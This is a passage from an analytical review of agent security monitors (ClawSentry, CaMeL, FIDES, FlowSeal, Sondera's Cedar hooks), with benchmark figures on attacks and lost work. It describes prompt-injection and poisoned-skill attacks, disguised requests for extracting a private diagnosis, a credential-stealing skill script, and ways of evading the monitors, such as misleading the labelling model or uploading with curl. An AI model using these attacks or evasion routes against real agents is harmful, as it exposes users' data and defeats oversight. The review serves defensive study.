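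|---|---|---|---|
| Codex, GPT-5.4 | 18.75% / 4.47% | 39.55% / 2.61% | 83.78% / 83.05% |
| Codex, GPT-5.5 | 29.38% / 4.09% | 39.86% / 8.40% | 87.01% / 84.75% |
| Claude Code, GLM-5.1 | 31.10% / 4.49% | 53.91% / 14.29% | 81.94% / 76.27% |
| Claude Code, MiniMax-M2.7 | 35.26% / 6.02% | 37.60% / 10.85% | 83.33% / 69.49% |
| Kimi CLI, Kimi-K2.5 | 34.66% / 5.63% | 27.74% / 6.82% | 79.22% / 64.41% |

The paper's summary features Codex with GPT-5.4, which had the largest reduction in contextual attacks (93%) and the smallest loss of completed tasks. With the other four combinations, ClawSentry prevented 71% to 79% of the contextual attacks that would have succeeded, and task success fell by 2 to 15 points. The reductions in attacks are still large, and Schmotz and colleagues, who built the benchmark, had no part in ClawSentry.

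Even the 2.61% is less certain than it looks, because Wang and colleagues left out runs that technical faults had interrupted. The percentages imply that 3 of 115 attacks succeeded with ClawSentry, compared with 53 of 134 without it. The full set has 139 contextual cases, so 24 are missing from the runs with ClawSentry. If all 24 attacks had succeeded, which is very unlikely, the rate would be 19%.

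The second benchmark was the full SkillSafetyBench, which Wang and colleagues call SkillsSafety.

| Agent and model | Attack success, without / with | Task success, without / with |
|---|---|---|
| Codex, GPT-5.4 | 44.5% / 12.50% | 38.7% / 25.66% |
| Codex, GPT-5.5 | 41.8% / 15.03% | 42.6% / 30.07% |
| Claude Code, GLM-5.1 | 33.5% / 12.40% | 37.4% / 23.14% |
| Claude Code, MiniMax-M2.7 | 34.2% / 9.09% | 20.6% / 15.58% |
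| Kimi CLI, Kimi-K2.5 | 49.7% / 10.20% | 31.0% / 16.33% |

Attack success fell from 33.5–49.7% without ClawSentry to 9.09–15.03% with it. Jin and colleagues published the figures without ClawSentry alongside the benchmark, so any change in the agents or test equipment between the two sets of runs would affect the comparison. For Claude Code with GLM-5.1, the figures with ClawSentry also cover only 121 of the 155 cases.

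For each case, the test software declared to ClawSentry which files the task had to read and write. Many of these files were in folders that ClawSentry's rules treat as sensitive. An operator can make the same kind of declaration in real use, but someone has to write it for each task. Without the declarations, ClawSentry would probably have blocked more legitimate work.

### Which parts made the difference

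Wang and colleagues switched off two parts of ClawSentry in turn on 60 SkillSafetyBench cases, using Codex with GPT-5.4.

| Version | Attack success rate | Task success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Complete | 12.73% | 25.45% |
| Without package review | 23.73% | 30.51% |
| Without the record of denied effects | 19.30% | 29.82% |

Both parts seem to help, the package review more so, but the percentages correspond to 7, 14 and 11 successful attacks, so neither difference would be distinguishable from chance if the runs were independent. Wang and colleagues didn't test the rules without the second and third tiers, so the experiment doesn't show how much the models add when they review actions.

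Across five reviewing models, attack success ranged from 11.11% (6 successful attacks) to 17.24% (10). The choice of reviewer therefore seems to matter less than having ClawSentry at all, though the sample is too small to rule out a sizeable difference between reviewers.

A separate experiment, using Claude Code with MiniMax-M3, compared three responses to a suspicious package. Attacks succeeded 8.47% of the time when the package was blocked, 10.53% when the agent received a safety note while it worked, and 24.56% when a caution was added to the package's documentation. The documentation warning was clearly a poor substitute for a block. Wang and colleagues argue that a safety note is also inherently weaker than a block because it arrives after the package has influenced the agent. They may be right, but the two results differed by only one attack, with six succeeding under the note and five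 under the block.

### What ClawSentry costs in completed work

ClawSentry rarely stopped agents from completing clean tasks with clean skills. Wang and colleagues gave 58 tasks to the four combinations that use Codex or Claude Code. The agents completed all of them without ClawSentry and 98.7% with it. The test left out Kimi CLI, which lost the most completed tasks on both attack benchmarks. The paper doesn't give the share of harmless actions that ClawSentry blocked. An agent can find another way after a wrong block and still complete its task, so that share could be well above 1.3%.

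The losses were much larger when an attacker had poisoned the package by altering it or the files around it. In the SkillSafetyBench results above, task success fell by 5.0 to 14.7 points. Since success rates were low to begin with, the agents lost between a quarter and nearly half of the tasks they would otherwise have completed.

To find out why, Wang and colleagues ran Codex with GPT-5.4 on 60 cases under four conditions.

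| Condition | Tasks completed (of 60) |
|---|---|
| No skill | 26 (43.3%) |
| Clean skill | 30 (50.0%) |
| Poisoned skill, no defence | 19 (31.7%) |
| Poisoned skill, with ClawSentry | 15 (25.0%) |

The attack alone lowered the score by 18.3 points, because a poisoned skill often disrupts the task it is supposed to help with. ClawSentry's blocking lowered it by another 6.7 points, or four tasks. Wang and colleagues stress that the attack accounts for about three quarters of the 25-point drop. However, the attack doesn't explain the losses of 5.0 to 14.7 points, because the agents in that comparison had poisoned packages both with and without ClawSentry. Those losses are comparable to the 6.7 points, which may be an underestimate because the same agent and model lost 13.0 points on the full benchmark.

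The four tasks are also a net figure. In the ten cases with misleading context, the agent completed five tasks with ClawSentry and three without it, presumably because ClawSentry kept it from following bad instructions by blocking an action. In the ten cases that attack the software the agent runs, it completed none with ClawSentry and three without it.

Some of these losses come from how the tests ran. When ClawSentry deferred an action to a person, nobody was there to answer, so the software treated every deferral as a block. A user who approved the legitimate actions would get more work done but would have to answer more prompts.

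The agent completed 15 tasks with a poisoned skill and ClawSentry, compared with 26 with no skill. By the time ClawSentry blocks something, the agent may already have read the hostile instructions and based its plan on them. Wang and colleagues conclude that the best time to reject a package is before the session starts, ideally in the marketplace. The figures support this, since an agent that never received the package would probably do about as well as one with no skill.

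### Review volume, with no delay in seconds

ClawSentry's rules handled 8,310 actions and other events in 300 runs (60 cases with each of the five reviewers). Of these events, 1,036 (12.5%) went to the second tier and 114 (1.4%) to the third. These 1,150 reviews equal 13.8% of the events, and the share was similar for every reviewer, from 12.2% to 15.5%.

This understates the models' workload. It leaves out 689 package reviews, more than two per run, although the rules will have settled some of those without a model. It also counts each third-tier investigation as one review, though the model may take several turns. But all the cases contained attacks, so ordinary work might need fewer reviews.

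Wang and colleagues report the number of reviews but not how long they took. They argue that waiting times depend mostly on the company that hosts the model. That is a fair reason not to generalise from one set of timings, but the paper still gives users no measurement of the delay.

The documentation for the earlier release does give targets: under 0.3 milliseconds for the rules, 3 seconds for the second tier and 30 seconds for the third. If every review took its full allowance, the mean delay per event would be

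0.0003 + (0.125 × 3) + (0.014 × 30) = about 0.8 seconds

In that case, seven out of eight actions would wait less than a millisecond, and about 1 in 73 would wait half a minute. Real reviews may be faster or slower than the targets, and package reviews would add to the total.

### Attacks written without ClawSentry in mind

Neither benchmark includes attacks written to get past ClawSentry, as Wang and colleagues acknowledge. The code and review rules are public, so an attacker could study them and adjust a package until it passed. The attack success rate could then be much higher than the published 9% to 15%.

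Even a simple variation, such as moving an injection within a file, helps an attacker. Schmotz and colleagues placed 36 obvious injections at five positions in a skill file. With GPT-5.2-Codex and no defence like ClawSentry, 61.1% succeeded in at least one position. On a larger set of 82 injections, single attempts succeeded 42.7% of the time.

The reviewing models have only read-only tools, so an attacker who deceives one can't use it to run commands or change files. But if the deceived reviewer wrongly clears an action, the agent will still carry it out.

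## Information flow rules: FlowSeal and earlier designs

An information flow rule uses only labels recording where data came from and who may read it, so an attacker can't change its result with persuasive wording, which might deceive ClawSentry's reviewing models. Google DeepMind's CaMeL and Microsoft's FIDES, both from 2025, use such rules against prompt injection. FlowSeal, from September 2026, uses them to keep a personal assistant from giving private records to people who have no right to see them.

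### Labels and how they combine

A confidentiality label specifies who may read a piece of data. The simplest version has two values, public and secret, and a more detailed one lists the permitted readers. An integrity label marks data as trusted or untrusted, where "untrusted" means an attacker could have written it.

When an agent mixes data, the result takes the stricter label of each kind. *APPA* (2026), which describes a flow control system for agents, writes the rule as

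(R, t) ∧ (R′, t′) = (R ∩ R′, min(t, t′))

where R and R′ are the sets of permitted readers and t and t′ are levels of trust. If Ana, Ben and Cara may read one document and Ben, Cara and Dan may read another, only Ben and Cara may read a summary of both. If either document is untrusted, so is the summary.

Nobody can reliably tell which parts of a language model's input influenced its output, so information flow designs usually assume that all of them did. Any tool call the model requests then carries the combined label of everything in its context.

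### One email in four situations

Suppose Ana asks an assistant to check Ben's sick-leave record, look up the legal limit online and email someone the number of sick days Ben has left. The record is trusted, and only Ana and Ben may read it. The web page is public but untrusted. Once the assistant has read both, its context is untrusted, and only Ana and Ben may read any output based on it.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) describe two basic rules in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. For the email, the confidentiality rule requires every recipient to be permitted to read the data, and the integrity rule requires the decision to send it to come from a trusted context. A developer can require the email to satisfy both rules or at least one.

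| Recipient | Assistant has read | Recipient may read the data | Context is trusted | Either rule is enough | Both rules required |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ben | record | yes | yes | allow | allow |
| Ben | record and web page | yes | no | allow | block |
| Outside accountant | record | no | yes | allow | block |
| Outside accountant | record and web page | no | no | block | block |

In the third row, the accountant isn't a permitted reader, but no untrusted text could have prompted the email, so the either-rule version treats it as Ana's own decision. In the fourth row, the web page could have prompted it, so both versions block the email.

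The stricter version blocks the task in the second row, which is the one Ana would most likely want. The either-rule version allows it, but an injection on the web page could then make the email give the wrong number of days, though it couldn't send the record to anyone new.

### Lifting a label

Labels only get stricter as data mixes, so an agent that reads enough can eventually do little. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) calls the end point label explosion, in which every piece of data carries every label and the labels no longer distinguish anything. Most systems therefore allow exceptions. Declassification lets a system release chosen confidential data, and endorsement lets it treat chosen untrusted data as trusted.

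A person can grant the exception. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, give the example of an email that lists ten tasks. If the user endorses the email, the agent can do all ten without asking again. Otherwise, the user may have to approve each one after the agent reads the email. *Agent libOS* (2026) limits the damage from a mistaken release by making each release valid only once, for one recipient and one exact text.

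In FIDES, a second model with no tools can read untrusted text and answer in a set format, such as yes or no. An injection in that text could make the answer wrong, but one bit is too little to carry an instruction. A fixed rule can therefore accept a yes-or-no answer where it would reject free text.

FlowSeal lets a model decide whether to allow a release, which makes its guarantee weaker. In Agent libOS, classifiers can veto a release or refer it to someone, but they can't approve one.

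### How CaMeL and FIDES keep untrusted text from the planner

Both systems build on a design that Willison proposed in 2023. In that design, one model plans the work and requests tool calls, and a second, quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools.

Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, explain how CaMeL applies this. The planning model turns the user's request into a short program in a restricted form of Python before it receives any outside data. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. If the program needs Bob's email address from a chat log, the quarantined model extracts it. The interpreter stores the address with labels for its sources and permitted readers, then checks those labels against the policies before each tool call.

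According to *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026), the resulting guarantee is that untrusted data can affect which branch of the program runs but can't add a step that the planner didn't write. This holds even without policies. The policies deal with attacks in which the steps are right but the data is wrong, such as a chat message that gives an attacker's address as Bob's. Sending the text through the quarantined model doesn't remove this danger, so the output has to keep the input's labels. *SPA* (2026) requires the same in its design.

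A complete plan made in advance can't handle a request like "do everything on my to-do list", because the steps depend on the list. FIDES plans one step at a time. It replaces untrusted results with variable names, which the planner can pass to a tool without reading the contents. The planner may read the contents of a variable, but the planner's context then becomes untrusted and the rules forbid many later actions.

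Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES can prevent confidential data from flowing directly to a forbidden place. The proof doesn't cover what an observer could infer from the agent's choice of actions. For example, if an assistant books a clinic visit only when a record shows an illness, the booking reveals the illness without copying any of the record. To prevent this too, FIDES would have to forbid almost every publicly visible action after the agent reads something confidential.

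Both guarantees assume that the user, the planning model and the tools are trustworthy, and that someone has set the labels and policies correctly. If the software labels installed skills as trusted, neither guarantee would cover a poisoned skill like those in the ClawSentry tests.

CaMeL's guarantee can also fail when agents give each other work. Peters-Gill and colleagues connected three CaMeL agents and asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applicants on Slack. An injection in the database reached the coordinating agent as untrusted data. That agent put the summary into its request to a third agent, which treated the whole request as a trusted instruction and also emailed the data to the attacker.

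The proposed solution is to send instructions and data between agents through separate channels. On a multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent and 0.0% with separate channels. Protecting each agent separately stopped nearly all the benchmark's attacks but failed against the attack designed to exploit the gap.

### Task success on AgentDojo

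Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with an attacker who knows which tools the agent has. With GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded without rules and none succeeded with FIDES's rules. AgentDojo's scoring marked three attacks against FIDES as successful, but Costa and colleagues inspected them and disagreed. They didn't count attacks that only changed the wording of an answer, since flow rules aren't meant to stop those.

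The table shows the percentage of ordinary tasks completed when there was no attack. The "one context label" agent applies the same kinds of rule but hides nothing from the planner.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, no rules | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o, one context label | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
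| o1, no rules | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| o1, FIDES | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

The second row shows the drawback of coarse labels. After the agent reads one Slack message, its entire context is labeled untrusted, so the rules block many harmless actions that have nothing to do with the message. Travel tasks avoided this problem because the rules allow many travel tools even in untrusted contexts. Labeling a whole session, as Sondera's monitor does, risks blocking harmless actions in the same way.

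FIDES labels individual fields, such as the body of an email, which recovers much of the lost work. Costa and colleagues report that FIDES completes 8% more tasks with GPT-4o and 16% more with o1 than a basic agent with a single context label. Compared with no rules, however, average success across the four areas fell from 84% to 50% with GPT-4o and from 84% to 61% with o1.

Some of these failures are intended. Several banking tasks require the agent to follow instructions in a file, and a rule that ignores content can't distinguish the user's real bill from a forged one. Other failures happened because GPT-4o confused variable names or opened variables unnecessarily. o1 made better use of the system. Costa and colleagues don't measure FIDES's overhead, but they note that each query to the quarantined model adds a turn, which takes time and tokens.

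*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL stops nearly all AgentDojo attacks with comparable task performance. "Comparable" seems generous, since Kolluri and colleagues say such systems reduce task completion by up to 30%, and CaMeL reduced it by 21.6 points in Sharma and colleagues' test.

Kolluri and colleagues argue that these comparisons are unfair to flow rules, because many real products ask a person before any consequential action. They therefore counted a task as completed only if the agent needed no approval. With the model o3-mini, an agent that always had to ask before such actions completed 24.3% of tasks, compared with 50.1% for FIDES and 59.1% for Prudentia, a version of FIDES that tells the planner about the rules. This is a good argument for flow rules over constant prompts, but a weaker one for flow rules over a classifier like auto mode's, which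 also removes most prompts.

### The attacks FlowSeal is meant to stop

Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026), in *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, built FlowSeal for attackers who don't need an injection. In their main example, Jane's assistant has access to Mark's mental-health diagnosis, and Mark's ex-wife Emily wants it. They devised three attacks, all of which disguise the request:

- In the workspace attack, Emily shares a half-finished document and asks Jane to fill in her section.
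- In the clean-up attack, Emily lists true and false diagnoses and asks Jane to delete the wrong ones. The entries that remain reveal the truth.
- In the two-channel attack, an email asks Jane to reply only "completed", while a shared page asks for the details.

Existing defences often instruct the assistant to get consent when someone requests private information. These attacks succeed when the assistant doesn't recognise the task as such a request, so it never asks for consent.

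### Fixed rules and one model call

Before FlowSeal can protect a record, someone has to register it with its owner and the people allowed to receive it. Software can do some of this from contact lists and access settings. FlowSeal then intercepts every tool call:

1. If the tool reads data, FlowSeal runs it and notes any protected records in the result.
2. If the tool writes or shares something, FlowSeal looks up the recipient. It allows trusted recipients and blocks those on a blocklist.
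3. For anyone else, it looks for tainted records that this recipient isn't authorised to receive. If there are none, it allows the call.
4. Otherwise, it sends those records and the proposed text to a separate model, which answers "SAFE" or "BLOCKED".

The first three steps are fixed rules, and the model makes only the final decision. The model doesn't receive the conversation, so Emily can't tell it that this is just teamwork, although the proposed text may still contain her words. The assistant can also ask a record's owner for consent. If the owner agrees, FlowSeal can release that record to that recipient.

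All registered records count as tainted from the start, so nearly every message to an unknown recipient goes to the model. The labels determine when this check runs, but in practice what gets out depends on the model's answer, so Shim and colleagues' proof rules out a leak only if the model doesn't wrongly answer "SAFE".

Shim and colleagues describe FIDES as leaving its enforcement to a language model, but FIDES also checks its policies in ordinary code before each call. Its list of permitted readers could in principle stop Emily too. They didn't test FIDES, partly because it didn't fit their test software.

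### Leaks and lost work with FlowSeal

The main test used 105 scenarios, each run three times, with DeepSeek-V3.2 as the assistant and DeepSeek-R1 judging whether private items had leaked. Shim and colleagues also rewrote these scenarios as harmless requests. Both comparison defences are prompts that tell the assistant to verify consent, and the second adds a strict sequence of identity checks.

| | Consent prompt | Stricter consent prompt | FlowSeal |
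|---|---|---|---|
| Items leaked, workspace attack | 31.8% | 52.2% | 0.5% |
| Items leaked, clean-up attack | 54.7% | 75.6% | 2.3% |
| Items leaked, two-channel attack | 13.3% | 43.8% | 2.2% |
| Harmless tasks completed | 75.9% | 44.7% | 72.4% |

The paper's summary highlights the drop from 52.2% to 0.5%, but the simpler prompt is a fairer comparison because it leaked less and completed more tasks. FlowSeal still leaked far less than either and completed only slightly fewer harmless tasks. Shim and colleagues give no leak rate for an assistant without any defence. On 378 scenarios adapted from another benchmark, PrivacyLens, FlowSeal leaked 0.5% of items, and on 571 from ConVerse it leaked 3.3%. In one ConVerse failure, it released a health detail that nobody had registered.

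Shim and colleagues also removed or changed one part of FlowSeal at a time.

| Version | Items leaked, workspace attack | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Complete | 0.5% | 72.4% |
| Without the prompt explaining FlowSeal to the assistant | 8.8% | 74.4% |
| Without the interceptor | 28.4% | 81.2% |
| Model check always answers "BLOCKED" | 1.3% | 0.0% |
| Model check always answers "SAFE" | 24.9% | 79.4% |

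When every model check returned "BLOCKED", the assistant completed no harmless tasks, because every recipient was unknown and the owners ignored requests for consent. The labels alone are therefore too coarse to use here, and FlowSeal depends on the model to allow legitimate messages.

Removing the prompt increased leaks from 0.5% to 8.8%, although Shim and colleagues say it isn't critical for security because the interceptor blocks leaks anyway. The 8.8% is the better estimate of the leak rate when the assistant doesn't cooperate. The 1.3% is odd, since nothing should have reached an unknown recipient. Either some leaks took a route that FlowSeal didn't cover or the judging model made mistakes.

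Shim and colleagues don't report false positive or false negative rates for individual messages. They say that the model check mainly misses paraphrases, such as a private fact reworded inside a longer sentence, and that it sometimes blocks a message that mentions a record without revealing its contents. Comparing the complete system with the version that always answers "SAFE" suggests that the check lowers performance on harmless tasks by about 7 points.

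The losses were larger in another test, where the request was legitimate and the owner would consent if asked. FlowSeal's assistant delivered only 32.7% of the requested items, compared with 61.0% to 85.6% for the other defences tested. Shim and colleagues attribute this to the assistant asking for consent less often. That explains only part of the gap, because the assistant asked about 28% less often than it did with the simpler consent prompt but delivered about half as much.

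In another test, the clean-up attack was run on real Gmail and Notion accounts. PrivacyChecker, which asks a model for advice but doesn't block anything, leaked 34.7% of items, and FlowSeal leaked none. The test counted only facts that appeared word for word, so it would have missed the paraphrases that FlowSeal has most trouble with.

### Overhead, and a pattern matcher before the model

FlowSeal raised the average cost of a run from $0.092 to $0.109 and the average time by 37%, from 5.44 to 7.45 seconds. Shim and colleagues measured this during the workspace attack, when the assistant often had to rewrite a blocked message and try again. Both increases would probably be smaller in ordinary work with fewer blocks.

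The times are hard to reconcile with the number of model calls, which rose from 46.7 to 57.1 per run. Making 46.7 calls in 5.44 seconds would mean one every 0.12 seconds, which is implausibly fast. The times may be the average gap between calls, which is what Shim and colleagues report for the live test. In that case, a whole run would take about 67% longer with FlowSeal.

To reduce both delay and errors, Shim and colleagues propose running a pattern matcher for personal data before the model check. They haven't built it, and its value would depend on whether it could only block messages or also clear them. It could immediately block a message containing a phone number from a protected record. But if it also cleared messages in which it found no personal data, it would let through paraphrased data, which Shim and colleagues criticise pattern-based detectors for missing.

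A matcher that can only block messages would be safe to add, but it would save time mainly during attacks, since harmless messages would still have to wait for the model. To catch a diagnosis, it would also have to compare the message with the records, because a phrase like "generalised anxiety disorder", unlike a phone number, has no fixed format.

### Attacks with nothing to recognise

The vendor's record with a false phone number, from Liang and colleagues' benchmark, contains nothing that would let a classifier recognise the forgery. A flow rule doesn't have to detect it. The rule labels the number untrusted, however plausible it looks, because it came from a source an attacker could have changed. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) makes the general point that unsafe behaviour can come from what influenced an action as well as from its content.

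This works only if the policy checks the label on the detail that matters. For payments on AgentDojo, FIDES checked whether the decision to pay came from a trusted context but ignored the labels on the payment details. If a user asked the agent to pay a bill and the bill contained a forged account number, the policy would allow the payment. Requiring a trusted account number would block that payment, but it would also block payment of every genuine bill from a new supplier until the user endorsed the number.

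### Deletions and other actions that send nothing

Confidentiality rules compare data with its recipients, so they don't apply to deleting a file, which has no recipient. FlowSeal checks only tools that its operator has classed as writing or sharing, so a delete tool outside those classes could erase a whole mailbox unchecked.

Integrity rules can block some harmful deletions. FIDES allows its agent to delete a file only in a trusted context, so an injection on a web page can't cause a deletion. But if the agent misunderstands the user and tries to delete the wrong folder, the rule allows it because no untrusted text is involved. Anthropic designed auto mode's classifier mainly for mistakes of this kind.

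*SafeFlow* (2026) adds a label for destructive writes and holds them back if the task doesn't need them or nobody has authorised the target. Those conditions concern purpose and permission, which can't be determined from labels on data. Nikolaou and colleagues' extension of CaMeL checks the order of steps in a plan before anything runs. It can reject a plan that disconnects a computer from the network without first getting approval, if someone has written a rule for that action. Kolluri and colleagues conclude that flow rules can replace human approval as a defence against attacks, but not as a check on the model's own mistakes.

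## Sondera's hooks: signatures, a safeguard model and flow labels in one monitor

A flow rule works only on labelled data. FlowSeal's users have to register each private record in advance, which isn't practical for a coding agent that might open any file on a developer's machine. Sondera, a company that makes controls for AI agents, has a language model assign the labels while the agent works. Its open-source monitor for coding agents applies fixed rules to these labels and to pattern matches to reach a verdict. Matt Maisel, Sondera's chief technology officer, presented the monitor on 3 March 2026 at Unprompted, a conference on AI security.

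### From hook to verdict

The monitor uses the hooks of Claude Code, Cursor, GitHub Copilot CLI and Gemini CLI. In *Hooking Coding Agents with the Cedar Policy Language*, the written version of his talk, Maisel describes an adapter for each product. Like ClawSentry's adapters, each one converts the hook's record into a common format and sends it to a service on the developer's machine.

The common format has four types of event. Actions include shell commands and file writes, and observations are the results returned to the agent. The monitor can therefore check both what an agent does and what it reads. Control events include user prompts and the start of a subagent, and state events cover housekeeping such as condensing the agent's memory.

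Before it decides anything, the service attaches attributes to the event. Sondera's guide to writing policies lists three main kinds:

- YARA signatures supply the number of matches, a severity from 0 to 4 and the categories of threat, such as credential access, exfiltration or obfuscation.
- A policy model lists violations of a secure-coding policy, such as exposed secrets or injection flaws.
- A sensitivity label marks the data as Public, Internal, Confidential or HighlyConfidential. The highest label covers personal data, credentials and trade secrets.

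Maisel used gpt-oss-safeguard-20b to assign the sensitivity labels, according to *Hooking Coding Agents with Cedar* (2026), a set of outside notes on the talk.

The service then passes the event and its attributes to Cedar, the access-rule language from Jing and colleagues' policy-engine test. A Cedar rule permits or forbids an action under stated conditions, and a single matching "forbid" overrides every "permit". This is the rule in Sondera's guide that stops web access after an agent has read highly confidential data:

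```
forbid (principal, action == Action::"WebFetch", resource)
when { resource.label == Label::"HighlyConfidential" };
```

The "resource" here is the whole session. Cedar keeps no state between requests, so the service stores the session's label and taints and passes them to Cedar with each request.

Cedar's tools can find rules that contradict each other or can never take effect. This makes it safer to have a model draft the rules, which Maisel suggests because writing them by hand is tedious. But the tools can't check whether the labels are correct.

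### A script that collects passwords and a session with personal data

In one of Maisel's demonstrations, a Cursor user installs a skill advertised as a tool for calculating code metrics from a public marketplace. Its script, `metrics.py`, collects the machine's environment variables, which often contain passwords and access keys, and sends them to an outside address. The monitor blocks the shell command that would start the script, even though nothing in the command itself is suspicious, as with `report.py`.

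The two accounts of the talk differ on what triggered the block. According to the outside notes, the service scanned `metrics.py` and found two YARA patterns, one for collecting environment variables and one for an outgoing request. According to Maisel, the session had a Confidential label and an exfiltration taint, which the policy model had set. Both could be true, since a single event can have all of these attributes.

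A rewritten script could get past the signatures, and the safeguard model's verdict could change from one run to the next.

The second demonstration uses Gemini CLI. The agent reads a file with a person's name, date of birth and address. The model labels the contents HighlyConfidential, and the session keeps this label. When the agent then tries to fetch a page from Google, the web rule blocks the request. The rule blocks every fetch, even of a harmless page, because a web address can itself carry data.

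In a third demonstration, in Claude Code, a rule blocks a database command that doesn't specify which rows to delete and so would delete every row in the table. The rule doesn't need a sensitivity label.

### When the label is missing

Sondera (2026) describes the signatures and Cedar rules as deterministic, and the model classifiers as optional and probabilistic. If a rule depends on a model's label, Cedar still applies the rule the same way every time, but a wrong label can produce a wrong result.

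If the model labels a customer list Internal instead of HighlyConfidential, the web rule doesn't fire. The guide's example policy permits everything that no rule forbids, so Cedar allows the agent to send the list out.

The web rule also covers only the agent's web-fetch tool. A `curl` command, or a Python script that opens its own connection, counts as a shell command. In sensitive sessions, the guide's example rule for shell commands applies only if the policy model has also found a violation. Unless a signature matches, the rule therefore stops a scripted upload only if the session has been marked as sensitive and the policy model finds a violation. If each judgement is right 90% of the time and their errors are independent, the rule stops 81% of such uploads. The version of the web rule in the outside notes also covers network commands, but the service would still have to detect that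 a script will use the network.

The more confidential files an agent reads, the less likely the session is to stay unrestricted, because one correct label is enough to restrict it. If the model has an independent 10% chance of missing each confidential file, the chance that it misses three out of three is 0.1%. But if the agent sends the first file out before opening the second, only the first file's label can block the transfer.

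An attacker may also be able to influence the model. Mondl, Maisel and Brock (2026), in *Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code*, argue that an attacker can't talk a deterministic policy engine into ignoring its rules. This is true of Cedar but not of the models that supply its attributes. Someone writing a hostile skill could include comments in its script to mislead the policy model that judges it. The sensitivity label on a user's own records is harder to influence, because an attacker would have to get text into the same event as the records.

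### When the label is wrong

A wrong HighlyConfidential label causes more disruption than a wrong block, because it affects every later web request in the session. If the model wrongly gives this label to a share *p* of harmless reads, and its errors are independent, the share of harmless sessions that have lost web access after *n* reads is

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

With a 1% error rate, 39% of sessions have lost it after 50 reads.

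| Harmless reads wrongly labelled | After 10 reads | After 50 reads | After 200 reads |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0.1% | 1% | 5% | 18% |
| 1% | 10% | 39% | 87% |
| 5% | 40% | 92% | nearly 100% |

If an agent makes one web request after each of its 50 reads, a labelling error rate of 1% blocks 22% of the requests. The model's false positive rate on single reads would therefore be a poor guide to how disruptive the monitor is to use.

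An error rate of 1% may be optimistic. In Jing and colleagues' test on access rules, gpt-oss-safeguard-20b wrongly denied 23% of lawful requests. That was a different task, so the figure can't be applied here, but it gives little reason to expect a rate far below 1%.

Real errors would not be independent. A model that mislabels a file will probably mislabel it again when the agent reopens it, so the table is too pessimistic for agents that keep returning to the same few files. Errors would also cluster, so a team whose test data consists of invented names and birth dates might lose web access in almost every session, while another team rarely would.

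The labels are also coarse, because the model labels a whole event rather than just its sensitive parts, as Maisel confirmed after the talk. One customer's address in a thousand-line log is enough to restrict the session, even if the agent needed only an error code from another line. Starting a new session would clear the label, but the agent would lose its context.

### Harmless work blocked by coarse labels

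Coarse labels can block harmless work. In *From Attack Surface to Defense Architecture*, a yes-or-no taint blocked ten of 12 harmless coding workflows. In a typical workflow, an agent reads an issue report, edits code and runs tests. The taint was stricter than Sondera's web rule because it also restricted file writes and shell commands, which a coding agent can hardly work without.

The same paper's own design uses four levels of trust and two of sensitivity. Under it, an agent that has read an issue report can still edit code and run tests in isolation. The design blocked none of 12 harmless workflows and, in a parallel test, stopped all 12 attack sequences. Its developers ran both tests, and with only 12 harmless cases, the actual false positive rate could be as high as about a quarter. Still, the result fits FIDES's gains from finer labels.

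Even correct labels can restrict too much. *Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) describes a monitor from Google DeepMind that runs each command in a disposable copy of the file system and tracks which files it opens. People assign the initial labels, so no model can get them wrong. On recordings of 1,590 harmless coding sessions, the monitor blocked 74 (4.7%). In 17 of these, a command such as a text search through every folder had opened files marked as sensitive. The monitor treated the agent as having read those files, whether or not the agent had used anything in them.

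Sondera's model labels the content of an event, so if a search opens a file but prints none of it, that file should not affect the label. But if the search prints one sensitive line, the whole output could receive the highest label.

### What Sondera has measured

Maisel demonstrated the hooks in his talk but gave no error rates, and he said measuring the delay was ongoing work. Sondera showed the hooks again at the Black Hat security conference in 2026, under the name GolemHalt. Trickest's *Inventory the policy corpus guarding your coding agents* (2026), an outside company's page about the tool, doesn't give error rates or delays either.

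If gpt-oss-safeguard took about 1.5 seconds per label, as it might for a short permission decision, labelling 50 reads would add about 75 seconds to a session. Labelling in the background would avoid this delay, but the agent could then make a web request before the label arrived.

Mondl and colleagues have since tested one part of Sondera's approach, the automatic writing of Cedar rules, on MedAgentBench, in which agents work with simulated medical records. Other researchers had written an 88-rule safety policy for it and turned 23 rules into code by hand. Mondl and colleagues had Gemini 3 Pro translate the policy into Cedar rules, which Cedar's tools and a second model checked. They also used Claude Opus 4.7 to copy further restrictions from the earlier team's code. Finally, they replayed recorded sessions against the combined rules.

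| Recorded sessions with an attempt to change a record | Blocked |
|---|---|
| Adversarial prompts | 99 of 99 (100%) |
| Ordinary tasks | 253 of 259 (97.7%) |

Open Source For You's *Sondera Open Sources AI Agent Policy Enforcement Harness* reports the score of 99 out of 99 but not the result for ordinary tasks. Together, the two results show that the rules blocked nearly every attempt to change a record, whatever its purpose. A single rule against all changes would also have scored 99 out of 99.

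The two rules that fired most often require the agent to restate the patient's details and to get confirmation before it changes a record. The recorded agents probably did neither, since the benchmark gives them a task to complete on their own. The blocks may therefore be correct under the policy, but developers would have to redesign an agent for it to get any work done. Mondl and colleagues set out to measure how much of the policy the rules covered, not whether the agent remained useful. They acknowledge, based on their field testing, that overly narrow rules lead developers to switch protection off.

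The experiment tested how Cedar rules behave when their inputs come straight from the recorded tool calls, which is the easier part of the problem. It did not include the coding hooks, the YARA signatures or the sensitivity labels.

### A layered defence of agent memory

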